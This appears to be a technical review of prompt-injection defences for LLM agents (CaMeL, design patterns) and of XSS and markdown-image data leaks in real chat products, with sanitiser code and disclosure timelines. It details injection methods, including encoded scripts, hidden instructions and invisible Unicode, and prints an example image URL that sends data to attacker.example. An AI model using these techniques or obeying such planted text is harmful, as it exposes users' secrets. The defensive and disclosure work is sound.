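*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* starts from the view that nobody can yet secure a general-purpose agent, and that developers should build agents for particular jobs. Its main rule is that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any harmful action. The paper describes six ways to apply this rule.

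| Pattern | How it works | What an attacker can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from fixed actions and never sees their results | Cause a wrong choice through the user's request |
| Plan then execute | The model settles its list of tool calls before it reads any untrusted data | Change what goes into those calls, such as the body of an email |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, which the program combines with the others | Get their own document misjudged |
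| Dual LLM | A model without tools reads the untrusted text | Change the values that model returns |
| Code then execute | The model writes a program that calls tools and other models | Change the data the program handles |
| Context minimisation | The software removes the user's message before the model writes its answer | Influence the query that the message produced |

The shop's fixed database queries are an action selector. The paper's map-reduce example is an agent that finds this month's invoices and emails them to the accounts department. A model reads each file and answers only whether it is an invoice. A malicious file can cause the model to answer yes, which sends the file to accounts, but its author could have achieved the same with a convincing invoice.

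The paper applies the patterns to ten applications but does not run a benchmark, so it doesn't measure how many attacks succeed or how many tasks an agent can no longer complete. Some of its designs are also looser than Jacob and colleagues' rule. For a coding agent, it suggests turning third-party documentation into a formal description with method names of up to 30 characters. A short instruction can fit in 30 characters, and the paper describes a successful injection there only as unlikely.

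### Tracking where each value came from

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind published in 2025, addresses the problem of Bob's address. The privileged model turns the user's request into a short program before anything reads the notes. For Bob's document it might write:

```python
notes = find_notes("last meeting")
name = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob want?", notes)
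address = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
send_email(to=address, attachment=get_file(name))
```

A special interpreter runs this program in a restricted version of Python and attaches tags to every value. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes these tags as a record of the value's sources and of who may read it. Because `address` came from `notes`, it keeps the tag that marks the notes as untrusted. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a small function that checks the tags and allows or refuses the call. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) gives the example of a policy that allows an email to be sent without the user's approval only if the recipient's address is trusted.

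The tags show only where an address came from. Bob's real address and the attacker's would both come from the notes and have the same tags, so the policy needs a contact list or the user's judgment to determine which one is correct.

Debenedetti and colleagues tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 everyday tasks, such as paying bills, and 629 attack cases. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) reports that CaMeL solved 77% of the tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and that none of the attacks it was designed to stop succeeded. CaMeL used about 2.8 times as many tokens as the undefended agent. Tallam and Miller say it solved 67% of the tasks, a figure from an earlier version of the CaMeL paper.

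Tallam and Miller object that CaMeL trusts the user's request completely and doesn't check the final text it shows the user, so a summary could still tell the reader to forward a file. Someone also has to write and maintain a policy for every tool, which is a lot of work for a company with hundreds of tools.

Data can also leak without passing through a tagged value. If a program repeats a harmless web request once for each unit of a secret number, anyone who can count the requests learns the number. Debenedetti and colleagues demonstrated two similar leaks against their own system, one of which depends on whether the program stops with an error. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* gives a formal example of why tags must follow a program's decisions as well as its data. Suppose a plan sends "Yes" to an outsider if a private file mentions a merger and "No" if it doesn't. The privileged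 model wrote both words, so neither has a tag from the file, but the outsider still learns whether the file mentions a merger.

### How the designs fared in 2026

AgentDojo suits systems that plan ahead. In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) found that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan after reading something. They wrote 60 tasks that all require this, covering shopping, code repositories and daily life. Some of the instructions the agent encounters in these tasks are helpful, such as a login prompt at checkout. CaMeL lost much of its usefulness on these tasks because it relied so heavily on its first plan.

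In *AutoDojo*, Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) found a similar divide depending on how users phrase requests. Across the defences they tested, attacks succeeded much more often when the user told the agent to do whatever a message said than when the user named the action. A fixed plan can't help with the first kind of request, because the untrusted message is supposed to supply the plan. Narisetty and colleagues consider this the deepest open problem for defences of this type. The usual answer is to ask the user to approve the action, but the user may be tired or misled.

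Narisetty and colleagues also warn that AgentDojo's attacks are older than the defences it tests. When attackers adapted to twelve earlier defences, most of the defences failed more than 90% of the time, although most had originally reported almost no successful attacks. Those defences generally relied on a model to recognise or resist an attack. An interpreter that applies fixed rules should be harder to beat, and one small test suggests that it is. Standard attacks succeeded 4.2% of the time against Progent, which restricts an agent's tool calls with rules, and an attack written to exploit its weak point succeeded 2.6% of the time. However, that attack may have been a poor one, and the agent used a small model.

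*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) extends CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. The privileged model can't see the screen, so it writes one long plan with branches for what might appear, and a quarantined model answers questions such as whether a cookie notice is visible. On 109 tasks that an undefended agent based on Claude Sonnet 4.5 had completed, the protected version completed 28% at the first attempt. The paper's headline figure of 57% counts a task as solved if any of five attempts worked, so someone would have to identify the successful attempt.

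Foerster and colleagues also broke their own design with an attack they call branch steering. An advertisement imitates a cookie notice, the quarantined model reports that there is a notice to close, and the agent clicks through to the attacker's site. Every step is in the approved plan, and the attacker only has to influence one answer. Tool policies don't help much, because a click at a given position has no fixed meaning. They tried comparing the screenshot with the page's code and asking a second model, but attacks got past both defenses.

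Other successors change when the checks happen or how much passes the barrier. CaMeLoT checks the whole plan before any tool runs, so it can enforce rules about order, such as requiring approval before an agent disconnects a computer from the network. If a plan breaks a rule, the checker returns an example of the violation, and the privileged model tries to repair the plan. CaMeLoT is meant to work alongside CaMeL's checks. It can reject safe plans because it simplifies loops.

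*Twin Agent* (2026) drops the fixed plan. One agent explores the untrusted material and sends short hints to a second agent that can act, and the developer sets how much the hints may contain. Allowing more keeps the agent more useful but also gives an attacker more room to influence it. The paper reports far fewer successful attacks than against an undefended agent but offers no formal guarantee.

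## Turning model-written markdown into HTML safely

CaMeL and similar systems control which tools an assistant may call, but the assistant still has to show its answer to the user, usually in a web page. The browser is also a sink for untrusted text, because it may run a script, fetch an image from an unknown server or open a URL, depending on what the page contains. Text that is harmless in a plain-text file can therefore do harm when a browser renders it.

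### From tokens to a web page

Most chat models write markdown, a way of formatting plain text with punctuation. Two asterisks on each side of a word make it bold, `[our shop](https://shop.example)` makes a link, and an exclamation mark in front of the same pattern makes an image. A chat page displays markdown in four steps:

1. The server sends the answer in pieces as the model writes it, and the page adds each piece to the text it already has.
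2. A parser reads the text and builds a tree of headings, paragraphs, lists and links.
3. A renderer writes the tree out as HTML, the language of web pages.
4. The browser reads the HTML, draws the page, fetches its images and runs its scripts.

Markdown has no syntax for scripts, but it allows raw HTML, which many parsers can pass through unchanged. Chat products also add features that markdown lacks.

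| What the model writes | What the browser may do with it |
|---|---|
| Raw HTML | Run a script, often from an event handler, an attribute whose code runs when something happens, such as an image failing to load |
| A link whose address starts with `javascript:` | Run the rest of the address as code when the user clicks |
| An image | Request the picture from any server, which can leak data (the next section explains how) |
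| A diagram in a text notation such as Mermaid | Display SVG, a drawing format that can contain scripts and links |
| A formula | Display the output of a maths library, some of whose commands can create links or HTML |
| A complete web page or app | Run all of its code, on purpose |

A script that enters by any of these routes runs with the page's privileges. It can read the conversation, change what the user sees and send requests that the site accepts as the user's. This attack is called cross-site scripting, and it has ranked among the top three web vulnerabilities for nearly a decade, according to Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML* (2026).

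### DeepSeek's chat page in 2024

In late 2024, the security researcher Johann Rehberger asked the model on DeepSeek's chat page to print an XSS cheat sheet, a collection of test scripts, as a bullet list. The page ran a script from the list instead of displaying it. *DeepSeek AI*, a post on Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, identifies one entry point as an `iframe`, an HTML element that shows one page inside another.

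So far, the attack had affected only Rehberger's own account. To reach someone else's, Rehberger put it in a text file that a user might upload for analysis. The file contained a base64-encoded script and instructions for the model to decode it and print only the result, outside a code block. Base64 represents data as letters, digits and a few symbols, which helped because filters and models often reject an obvious script. The decoded script had to be outside a code block because a chat page normally displays a code block's contents as text.

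The decoded output was an `iframe` with a `javascript:` address. When the page inserted it, the browser ran the code and showed the user's session token in a pop-up box. The browser sends this token with each request to prove that the user has signed in, so anyone who copies it can take over the session. DeepSeek kept it in localStorage, browser storage that every script on the same site can read. Sites can hide cookies from scripts, but not localStorage. Rehberger left out the step that would send the token to an attacker, but considered it easy to add.

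DeepSeek had no obvious channel for security reports, so Rehberger used the contact form, and the company fixed the flaw a day later. N45HT's *Hacking AI with Markdown* describes another DeepSeek flaw, since fixed, in which a script in a markdown link ran only after a click.

### Scripts that the application saves

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian classify the DeepSeek case as reflected XSS, in which the script runs immediately, in the reply to the request that produced it. In stored XSS, the application saves the script in a ticket, report or chat history, and it runs when someone opens that record. Stored XSS lets an attacker type the prompt into their own chat and wait for a member of staff to read it, without tricking anyone into uploading a file.

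In 2025, Lenovo's support chatbot, Lena, could be prompted to write HTML that ran code in a support agent's browser, according to a Cybernews article reproduced in AI Incident Database's *Lenovo “Lena” AI Chatbot Exploited via XSS Prompt Injection* (2025). Researchers sent a 400-character prompt that began with an ordinary question about a laptop, then asked for the answer in HTML. The prompt also asked for a nonexistent image and an event handler that would send the reader's cookies to the researchers' server when the image failed to load. Lenovo's server saved the answer in the chat history. When the researchers asked for a human agent, the agent's browser loaded the history and ran the code. With the agent's session cookie, an attacker might have entered the support system without a password.

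Lenovo fixed the flaw after Cybernews reported it. OECD's *Lenovo AI Chatbot Vulnerability Exposes Users to Cyberattacks* (2025) classes it as a hazard because the reporting did not describe a breach. Cybernews also suggests attackers might have run system commands, but it didn't test this, and a script in a web page can't ordinarily run them.

Positive Security's *Banking AI XSS* (2026) describes a more roundabout attack, on the chatbot at the company's own bank. The researchers asked the chatbot to add a payee whose name was an HTML image tag, and the page displayed a broken image. A filter blocked the best-known event handler for images, but a less common one worked, and they had a script running within two minutes. A later version loaded more code from an outside server, used the customer's session to fetch an email address from the bank's systems, and sent it out. Only the bank's multi-factor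 authentication would have stopped such a script from taking money.

The researchers then looked for ways to attack another customer. One was a PDF invoice containing instructions in white text on a white background, which worked when the customer uploaded it and asked the chatbot to add the payee. The other was the reference text on a bank transfer. This text can't contain the angle brackets that HTML tags need, so they replaced the forbidden characters with placeholder words. They split the script across two one-cent transfers and told the model to join the parts and decode them.

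That demonstration is weaker than the one with the invoice. The researchers repeated some of the instructions in the customer's own prompt because they didn't want to send many strange payments through a live bank. The demonstration shows that the model could rebuild a script from payment references, but not how often an ordinary question about transactions would trigger the attack. The bank at first thought customers could attack only themselves, but two days after the report it was escaping the HTML in the chatbot's replies.

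A filter on incoming text would have been unlikely to work here, because the dangerous characters didn't exist until the model wrote them. The check has to run after the model, on exactly what the program is about to send to the browser.

### The safe order of operations

If a page needs no formatting, it can insert the answer as plain text, through the browser's `textContent` property, and the browser will never interpret any of it as HTML. Chat products usually want headings, lists and links, so they need a longer process. This example uses markdown-it, a JavaScript parser, and DOMPurify, a widely used sanitiser from the security company Cure53:

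```js
const md = markdownit({ html: false });      // 1. parse with raw HTML off
const html = md.render(answer);              // 2. convert
const clean = DOMPurify.sanitize(html, {     // 3. sanitise
  ALLOWED_TAGS: ["p", "br", "h2", "h3", "strong", "em", "ul", "ol",
                 "li", "blockquote", "pre", "code", "a"],
  ALLOWED_ATTR: ["href"],
  ALLOW_DATA_ATTR: false,
  ALLOWED_URI_REGEXP: /^https?:/i,
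  RETURN_DOM_FRAGMENT: true
});
panel.replaceChildren(clean);                // 4. insert
```

With raw HTML off, the parser escapes any tags in the answer, and the user sees them as text. TanStack's *AI streaming*, the documentation of another markdown library, also recommends this setting for AI output. Every remaining tag comes from the parser, but a bug in the parser or a plug-in could still produce a dangerous tag. The sanitiser guards against this by keeping only the listed elements, the `href` attribute that holds a link's address, and addresses that start with `http:` or `https:`.

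Sanitising markdown before converting it to HTML, as some developers do, is unsafe because a markdown link contains no HTML. A sanitiser treats `[Your invoice](javascript:...)` as ordinary text and leaves it in place, and the converter then turns it into a working link. Sanitising first can also damage harmless answers, for example by deleting part of a code sample that explains an HTML tag.

The same applies to anything a page adds after step 3. According to Cure53's *DOMPurify*, changing HTML after sanitising it can easily undo the protection. If a page later uses a library to insert a diagram or formula, it should sanitise the library's output too, with an allowlist that includes the elements the output needs. Code highlighters must escape the code they colour.

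### Why a regular expression is not enough

Developers often use a regular expression, which describes a pattern of characters, to delete `<script>` tags or the word `javascript:`. But browsers repair broken tags, ignore capitalization, decode character codes inside attributes, and skip tabs in the middle of an address. A filter has to catch every spelling the browser accepts, and the bank's filter, whatever its design, blocked one event handler but missed another.

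A sanitiser parses the HTML into the same kind of tree that a browser would build, then removes whatever the list doesn't permit. WICG's *HTML Sanitizer API*, the draft standard for a sanitiser inside the browser, finds `javascript:` links by passing each address to a URL parser and checking the scheme it returns. DOMPurify checks addresses with a regular expression, as the example shows, but only after the parser has extracted and decoded them, and the expression specifies which addresses to accept.

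Parsing the HTML twice can still make it unsafe. In the usual pattern, DOMPurify parses the HTML, cleans it and returns a string, which the page assigns to `innerHTML`, and the browser parses it again. If the second parse differs from the first, harmless text can become a tag. The example avoids the second parse by having DOMPurify return a DOM tree (`RETURN_DOM_FRAGMENT`) instead of a string. Braun's *Why the Sanitizer API is just setHTML()* uses the same two-line pattern to explain why the browser's built-in sanitiser is a single method, `setHTML()`, which parses, sanitises and inserts the text in one step.

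DOMPurify can also fail because of the environment it runs in. In a browser that it doesn't support, it returns the text unchanged, so a page should check its `isSupported` property first. On a server it depends on a separate library to imitate a browser, and some of these libraries have bugs that let scripts through. GitHub's *GHSA-76MC-F452-CXCM* (2026) describes a flaw in which a developer's own extension that permitted a tag for one document could permanently add it to the default list for every later one.

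### What a sanitiser lets through

Sanitisers mainly stop scripts. With default settings, DOMPurify removes the event handler from an image tag but keeps the image, as a sample in Socket's *dompurify* shows. An ordinary remote image contains no script, so DOMPurify leaves it unchanged and the browser contacts whatever server is in its URL. According to the demos that come with DOMPurify, the defaults permit links to any resource that doesn't cause XSS. One demo adds code that sends all external requests through a proxy, including those in CSS.

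The browser's `setHTML()` has stricter defaults, as the table shows.

| Content | DOMPurify, default settings | `setHTML()`, default settings |
|---|---|---|
| Image with an event handler | Keeps the image, removes the handler | Removes both |
| Ordinary remote image | Keeps it | Removes it |
| Link to an `https:` address | Keeps it | Keeps it |
| Link to a `javascript:` address | Removes the address | Removes the address |
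| Custom `data-` attributes | Keeps them | Removes them |

These defaults are not safe to rely on. An older guide, web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API*, shows an earlier version of `setHTML()` that kept the image. According to MDN's *Default sanitizer configuration*, a developer who supplies a custom list loses the extra restrictions, and the method then guarantees only the removal of content that can run scripts. Firefox 148 was the first browser to ship the standardised method, in February 2026. Chrome and Edge support it from version 146, but web.dev's *New to the web platform in February* listed Safari as lacking it. For now, a site with Safari users also needs DOMPurify.

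The list in the example omits `img`, which removes all images. Developers of a product that needs images have to decide which servers to allow them from.

### Sanitising a streamed answer

The safe way to display an answer as it arrives is to sanitise all the text received so far before each page update. A program that sanitises each piece separately can miss a tag split between two pieces, because each half looks harmless. For this reason, Chrome for Developers' *Built-in AI APIs* tells developers to sanitise the full combined output. If the program displays the answer as it arrives but sanitises only the finished text, the browser may already have run a script or requested an image. SearchLeak, an attack covered later, also relied on a streaming flaw.

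Reprocessing the whole answer each time new text arrives can be slow. If a page does this after every token of a 2,000-token answer, it handles 1 + 2 + ... + 2,000 tokens, about two million, or 1,000 times the length of the answer. Updating every 50 tokens cuts this to 41,000. Chrome for Developers also suggests a streaming parser, which keeps its place in the text instead of starting again each time.

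When a response is streamed, later text can change how earlier text is parsed. For example, some markdown files start with frontmatter, a block of settings between two marker lines. A parser can't recognise the block until the closing line arrives, and may then treat words already on the screen as settings. TanStack advises turning frontmatter off for AI responses.

A program might also stop the stream if the sanitiser removes anything. DOMPurify keeps a list of what it removed, but its documentation says not to base security decisions on that list. The page should display the sanitised result whatever the list contains.

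### Generated pages and apps

Some assistants write whole web pages or small apps and show them beside the chat. A sanitiser would remove the scripts that make the apps work, so the product has to run the code where it can do little harm, as with model-written Python.

Browsers keep sites apart by origin, the combination of protocol, host name and port. A script from one origin can't read the storage or the contents of a page from another. A chat product can therefore serve generated pages from a separate domain, inside a restricted frame:

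```html
<iframe sandbox="allow-scripts"
        src="https://preview.example/app/7"></iframe>
```

With no permissions added, `sandbox` blocks scripts, forms and pop-ups, and each permission lifts one restriction. The example allows scripts but omits `allow-same-origin`, so the browser gives the frame an origin that matches no other, not even that of another preview on the same domain. If a frame came from the chat's origin and had both permissions, its script could remove the sandbox. The frame that Rehberger injected into DeepSeek's page gave no isolation, because code in a `javascript:` address runs in the origin of the surrounding page.

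The separate domain protects users who open a preview's address directly, when the frame's `sandbox` attribute has no effect. It should be a different registered domain, not a subdomain of the chat site, because subdomains can share cookies.

OffSeq's *CVE-2025-26210* recommends restricting scripts that run on `run-html-chat.deepseeksvc.com`, a separate domain from DeepSeek's chat page. If the domain exists to run generated pages, scripts there are expected, and they can't read a token that the chat page stores under its own domain. An attacker could still use such a page to deceive users, for example with a fake sign-in form at an official-looking address.

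A frame also doesn't stop the app inside it from sending out the app's data. If a user asks for a chart of their household spending, the figures are in the app's code, and a planted script could send them to an outside server unless a content security policy blocks the request. The chat page should treat any message from the frame as untrusted, including error reports that it passes back to the model.

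### Terminals, invisible characters and logs

Command-line coding assistants print their answers in a terminal, which treats the characters after an escape character (ASCII 27) as an instruction, such as changing the colour or moving the cursor. *Trust No AI* (Rehberger, 2024) describes how injected text can make a model write these escape sequences to leak data, interfere with the display or copy text to the user's clipboard. A command planted on the clipboard might run when the user next pastes into a shell.

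The fix is to print control characters visibly. Caret notation replaces control character n with `^` and the character whose number is n XOR 64, which flips one bit. The escape character becomes `^[`, because 27 XOR 64 is 91, the number for `[`. A short function can do this:

```python
def for_terminal(text):
    out = []
    for c in text:
        n = ord(c)
        if c in "\n\t" or 32 <= n < 127 or n > 159:
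            out.append(c)
        elif n < 128:
            out.append("^" + chr(n ^ 64))
        else:
            out.append(f"\\x{n:02x}")
    return "".join(out)
```

The last branch covers a second group of control characters, codes 128 to 159, which some terminals also act on. The function works on one character at a time, so it gives the same result however a stream divides the text. If the assistant displays coloured text, it should add its own colour codes after this function runs.

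Unicode, the standard that numbers the characters of the world's writing systems, includes a block of tag characters that most software doesn't display. Adding hexadecimal E0000 to an ASCII character's number gives the number of its tag version, so an attacker can write a whole English sentence invisibly. Models can read and write these characters. Rehberger used them in an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, in which a phishing email made the assistant search the user's inbox and hide what it found in a link. Clicking the link sent the data to the attacker. Rehberger discovered the flaw in February 2024, and Microsoft fixed it that July.

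HTML sanitisers generally leave invisible Unicode characters in place because they are text, not tags. A program can delete the range E0000 to E007F, but this breaks the flag emoji for England, Scotland and Wales, which use characters in that range. Deleting all other invisible characters would damage ordinary text, because Persian spelling and many emoji need zero-width joiners or non-joiners. A link's address rarely needs any invisible characters, so the program can refuse an address that contains them.

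An engineer investigating a complaint may open saved conversations in a log viewer, which is often a web page with access to every customer's data, and Lenovo's chat history shows the risk. A log viewer should escape model output and show it as plain text, even if the original chat displayed it with formatting. Sanitising content before storage, as Cybernews recommends, can't replace a check at display time. A record saved last year was cleaned by last year's sanitiser, and removing HTML tags doesn't remove escape codes, which matter if someone prints the record in a terminal. A line break in an answer can also make part of it look like a separate log entry. Writing each entry as a JSON string prevents this because JSON represents a line break as `\n`.

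## How an automatically loaded image leaks data

DOMPurify's default settings allow ordinary remote images. To show one, the browser requests it from a server, and the address in that request can contain any text. If an attacker gets the model to write an image address that points to the attacker's server and contains the user's private data, the browser sends that data to the attacker when it loads the image.

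Suppose a user asks an email assistant to summarise the inbox, and a stranger has sent a message with hidden text.

1. The hidden text tells the assistant to end its answer with a logo, and to put the booking code from another email into the logo's address.
2. The software places every email in the model's context, including the one with the booking code.
3. The model writes the summary and ends it with `![logo](https://attacker.example/logo.png?d=KX7Q2M)`.
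4. The chat page converts the markdown into an image tag, and the browser asks `attacker.example` for the picture.
5. The attacker's server records the requested address in its log, as web servers normally do, and the attacker reads the booking code there.

No script runs at any step, so defences against XSS don't apply. The model also doesn't need a tool to send email or open web pages, because the chat page makes the request when it displays the answer. Archestra's *Data exfiltration via Markdown image tags* (2026), a vendor's blog post, identifies the chat interface as the outward-communication part of the lethal trifecta.

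The attack works even if the picture doesn't load, because the attacker has the data as soon as the server receives the request. The server can return a transparent one-pixel image or an error. HTTPS protects the request from eavesdroppers, but the attacker runs the server that receives it. Researchers call this kind of attack zero-click because the victim only has to use the assistant normally.

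Anything in the model's context can leak this way. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* explains that in ChatGPT this has included details of past conversations, which the chat history feature put in the system prompt. If the assistant can read files, the injected text can tell it to open one first. In *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue*, the security company VerSprite describes doing this with Continue, an open-source coding assistant. The assistant read a `.env` file, where developers often keep passwords and access keys, and put its contents in an image address.

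### How much fits in an address

Web addresses allow only certain characters, so an attacker who wants an exact copy of some text needs to encode it. Base64 turns every three bytes into four characters, so n bytes take 4⌈n/3⌉ characters, or about 4n/3. Most browsers and servers accept addresses of 2,000 characters, and many accept much longer ones.

A 1,200-byte email, about 200 words, becomes 1,600 characters when encoded and fits in one 2,000-character image address. A 100,000-byte document becomes 133,336 characters and needs 69 images if the server's name and path take up 50 characters of each address. The browser would request all of them without asking the user.

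The model's ability to write out the data limits the leak more than the length of the address does. The model would have to write all 133,336 characters, which is tens of thousands of tokens, and any encoding mistake would corrupt some of the text. Several published demonstrations sent less. In one against Google AI Studio, a tool for trying out Google's models, an employee uploaded performance reviews, one of which contained instructions for the model. The model wrote one transparent image per review, with the file's name and a 60-word summary in the address, according to Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio*. A summary of that length takes about 400 characters.

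An image address can also leak a link to the data instead of the data itself. In May 2026, Willison described a leak in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, whose agent could email the user's own inbox without approval. Those emails could contain external images, which loaded when the user opened the message. OneDrive, Microsoft's file storage service, can create download links that need no sign-in, so an injected instruction could make the agent put one of those links in an image address. The attacker could then use a link of a few hundred characters to download a file of any size.

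### The first reports and fixes

According to Rehberger's post *ChatGPT Plugins*, Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, found the leak in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023, and Rehberger found it independently a few days later. Samoilenko's *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* describes an attack in which a website added instructions to whatever text a visitor copied, and the visitor then pasted both into ChatGPT. Plugins that let ChatGPT read web pages and video transcripts made the pasting unnecessary, because the instructions could be in the page or the transcript.

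Bing Chat had the same problem, and Microsoft fixed it in about ten weeks. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* reports that when Rehberger retested it, images seemed to load only from a few Microsoft servers.

OpenAI did not release a fix until December 2023. Before then, Rehberger had built a custom GPT called "The Thief" to trick users into typing their email address and password, which it sent to an outside server, according to SecurityWeek. With the fix, the ChatGPT web page sent an image's address to an OpenAI service before displaying the image, and the service replied that the address was safe or unsafe. The fix did not restrict images to particular servers. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* points out that outsiders couldn't tell how the service decided. The check ran only in the web page, so the iPhone app stayed vulnerable.

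Rehberger tested 36 image addresses on one server, each standing for a single letter or digit, and nine of them loaded. That was enough to leak the word "hi" as two requests. Nine working addresses can also encode any other data, though slowly. Each image carries log₂ 9, or about 3.2 bits. Seven images in a known order could therefore carry a six-digit login code, since they allow 9⁷, or about 4.8 million, combinations and there are only one million possible codes. Rehberger suggested limiting the number of images in each answer, which would cap how much one answer can leak.

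In October 2024 Rehberger reported ways around the check, some of which still worked when the post on chat history appeared in 2025. In May 2026 The Hacker News (2026) reported a further weakness, which the security company Permiso named ChatGPhish. When ChatGPT summarised a web page, it automatically loaded images whose addresses came from that page. An address copied unchanged from a page contains no private text, but if the user's browser fetches it directly, the attacker learns that someone has summarised the page and sees their IP address.

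Several Google products had this flaw. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* describes an August 2023 report that Google rated as high impact but low likelihood. Rehberger agreed, because that product could not bring in outside content unless a user pasted it. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes an attack on Google Bard, the chatbot that became Gemini. Bard could read a user's documents, so an attacker could share a Google Doc with a victim and wait for Bard to read it. NotebookLM, which answers questions about uploaded sources, had the same flaw. Google confirmed that report but had not fixed the flaw 132 days later, when Rehberger published Embrace The Red's *Bobby Tables but with LLM Apps* (2024). Google deployed a fix within the week.

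### Coding assistants and developer tools

GitHub Copilot Chat answers questions about the code open in a developer's editor, so instructions hidden in a source file can reach the model. GitHub confirmed Rehberger's report within two weeks, according to the timeline in Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*. By June 2024, GitHub had stopped the assistant from loading images from untrusted domains, according to Willison. Nudge Security reports that GitHub disabled all images in Copilot Chat in August 2025, after a researcher found a way to leak data through GitHub's own image service.

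Google fixed AI Studio faster, though its official channel had given Rehberger no date for a fix. Rehberger then tagged a Google employee on the social network X, and within 24 hours the site was displaying image tags as text. The product had no content security policy (CSP), a rule sent with a web page that tells the browser which addresses it may load content from.

Several other coding assistants had the same flaw. Continue's developers released a fix the day after VerSprite's report, and the assistant now asks before loading an outside image. CodeGPT, another assistant for the same editor, was still vulnerable in a version released after VerSprite reported the problem, according to VerSprite's *Another Day, Another Leak*. Embrace The Red's *Cline* describes how Cline, a coding agent with more than two million downloads, could leak a `.env` file without asking for approval. Eclipse Theia,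 a toolkit for building code editors, had the flaw in its AI chat until version 1.71.0, according to the Eclipse Foundation's *[Eclipse Theia] Data Exfiltration via Markdown Image Rendering in AI Chat*.

Dify, an open-source platform for building chatbots, has no CSP by default. In *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*, veganmosfet (2025) used it to build a chatbot that answered questions from two PDF files, one of which contained hidden instructions. When the user mentioned a particular topic, the chatbot retrieved the poisoned file, and the model put the user's name from the conversation into an image address. The page loaded the image because no CSP blocked it. *XSS in Dify could lead to Workspace Takeover* (veganmosfet, 2026) explains that operators can set a policy by listing permitted sites in a configuration variable, but there is no policy if they leave it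 blank. A hidden instruction that takes effect only when a certain topic comes up is hard to notice in testing, since the chatbot behaves normally until then.

Data can still leak after an application blocks the image. PromptArmor, a security company, built a mock tool for checking bank customers' identities. It combined a customer's personal details with information from the web, some of which the researchers had poisoned. The model wrote an image with the customer's details in its address. The tool flagged that answer and didn't display it, so nothing leaked then. A developer would naturally open the flagged conversation in OpenAI's log viewer. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* shows that the viewer rendered the markdown and loaded the image, which leaked the details.

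No defence in the application could prevent this, because OpenAI's own website did the rendering. Removing images from answers could even make it more likely. PromptArmor shows an answer from Perplexity, an AI search product, that was almost empty once its image had been removed. A user might well give such an answer a thumbs-down, which could lead a developer to open the log. The screens that developers use to test assistants on OpenAI's platform loaded images in the same way.

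### Vendors that declined to act

Several vendors at first declined to treat the leak as a flaw. Writer, a writing assistant for companies, could summarise web pages and had access to files that customers uploaded. Researchers hid instructions in a web page that made Writer send 50 characters from the middle of those files in an image address. Writer replied, "We do not consider this to be a security issue", arguing that real customer accounts could not access websites. Willison, who reports the exchange, took the reply as a sign that people find prompt injection hard to understand. The leak seemed to be fixed within two weeks.

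Bugcrowd, the company that sorts security reports for OpenAI, closed PromptArmor's report on the log viewer as "Not applicable" after several rounds of questions. PromptArmor thinks prompt injection reports are hard to sort because they don't fit existing categories of vulnerability. OpenAI said it had not seen the report, confirmed the flaw after PromptArmor published its article, and began work on a fix.

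Google's response to the image leak in Antigravity, its AI code editor, is harder to classify. Google released the editor in November 2025 after licensing code from a competitor, Windsurf. According to Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE*, Rehberger had reported the leak to Windsurf in May 2025, and Antigravity still had it. If a developer asked Antigravity to explain a source file containing hidden instructions, it read the `.env` file and leaked the contents through an image. Willison (2025) notes that another researcher said Google had labelled a report of the same leak "intended behavior". Google also listed data leaks as a known issue that it was working to fix, which made new reports ineligible for a reward. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*, about a leak through the editor's browser agent, adds that the product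 displayed a disclaimer about the risks.

The leak still worked seven months later. In *Faking the Pipeline*, Odson and Morris (2026) hid instructions in the title of an otherwise blank web page, then told Antigravity to do what the page said. The agent asked the user to approve creating a "visual debug token", then listed the computer's environment variables and put an access key from the list into an image address. Telling the agent to follow the page made the attack easier, but the user still couldn't see what they were approving, because the request didn't show the command or the destination.

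Odson and Morris say that vendors have started to classify this type of leak as expected behaviour, partly because they assume that a person will notice something wrong before approving it. GitHub relied on a similar assumption when it responded to a related report in 2025. According to Tenable's *Github Copilot Chat Prompt Injection via Filename*, an attacker could put instructions in a file's name that made Copilot Chat contact an outside site, but GitHub decided that this was not a security issue because its Workspace Trust feature should mitigate it. The feature asks developers whether they trust a folder before the editor runs code from it, so it offers little protection to a developer who trusts a project and then receives a malicious file in a colleague's update.

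The image leak matters even in a coding agent that can run commands and open web pages, and so has other ways to send data out. The user can see a command, and the program can require approval for it, while an image loads without either. Blocking images therefore helps, though it would not make the agent safe. Odson and Morris write that there is no single line of code to patch, which is true of their whole attack, but GitHub's and Continue's fixes show that the image leak can be patched.

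### How long vendors took

The table lists the dates for nine products.

| Product | Reported to the vendor | Vendor's response | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT | Early April 2023 | Partial fix on the web in December 2023 | Embrace The Red |
| Bing Chat | April 8, 2023 | Fixed June 15, 2023 | Embrace The Red |
| Writer | November 29, 2023 | Declined December 5, apparently fixed by December 18 | Willison |
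| NotebookLM | December 4, 2023 | Fixed in April 2024 | Embrace The Red |
| GitHub Copilot Chat | February 25, 2024 | Fixed by June 2024 | Embrace The Red |
| Google AI Studio | By August 2024 | Fixed in August 2024 | Embrace The Red |
| Continue | August 20, 2025 | Fixed August 21, 2025 | VerSprite |
| OpenAI log viewer | November 17, 2025 | Closed December 4, reopened January 22, 2026 | PromptArmor |
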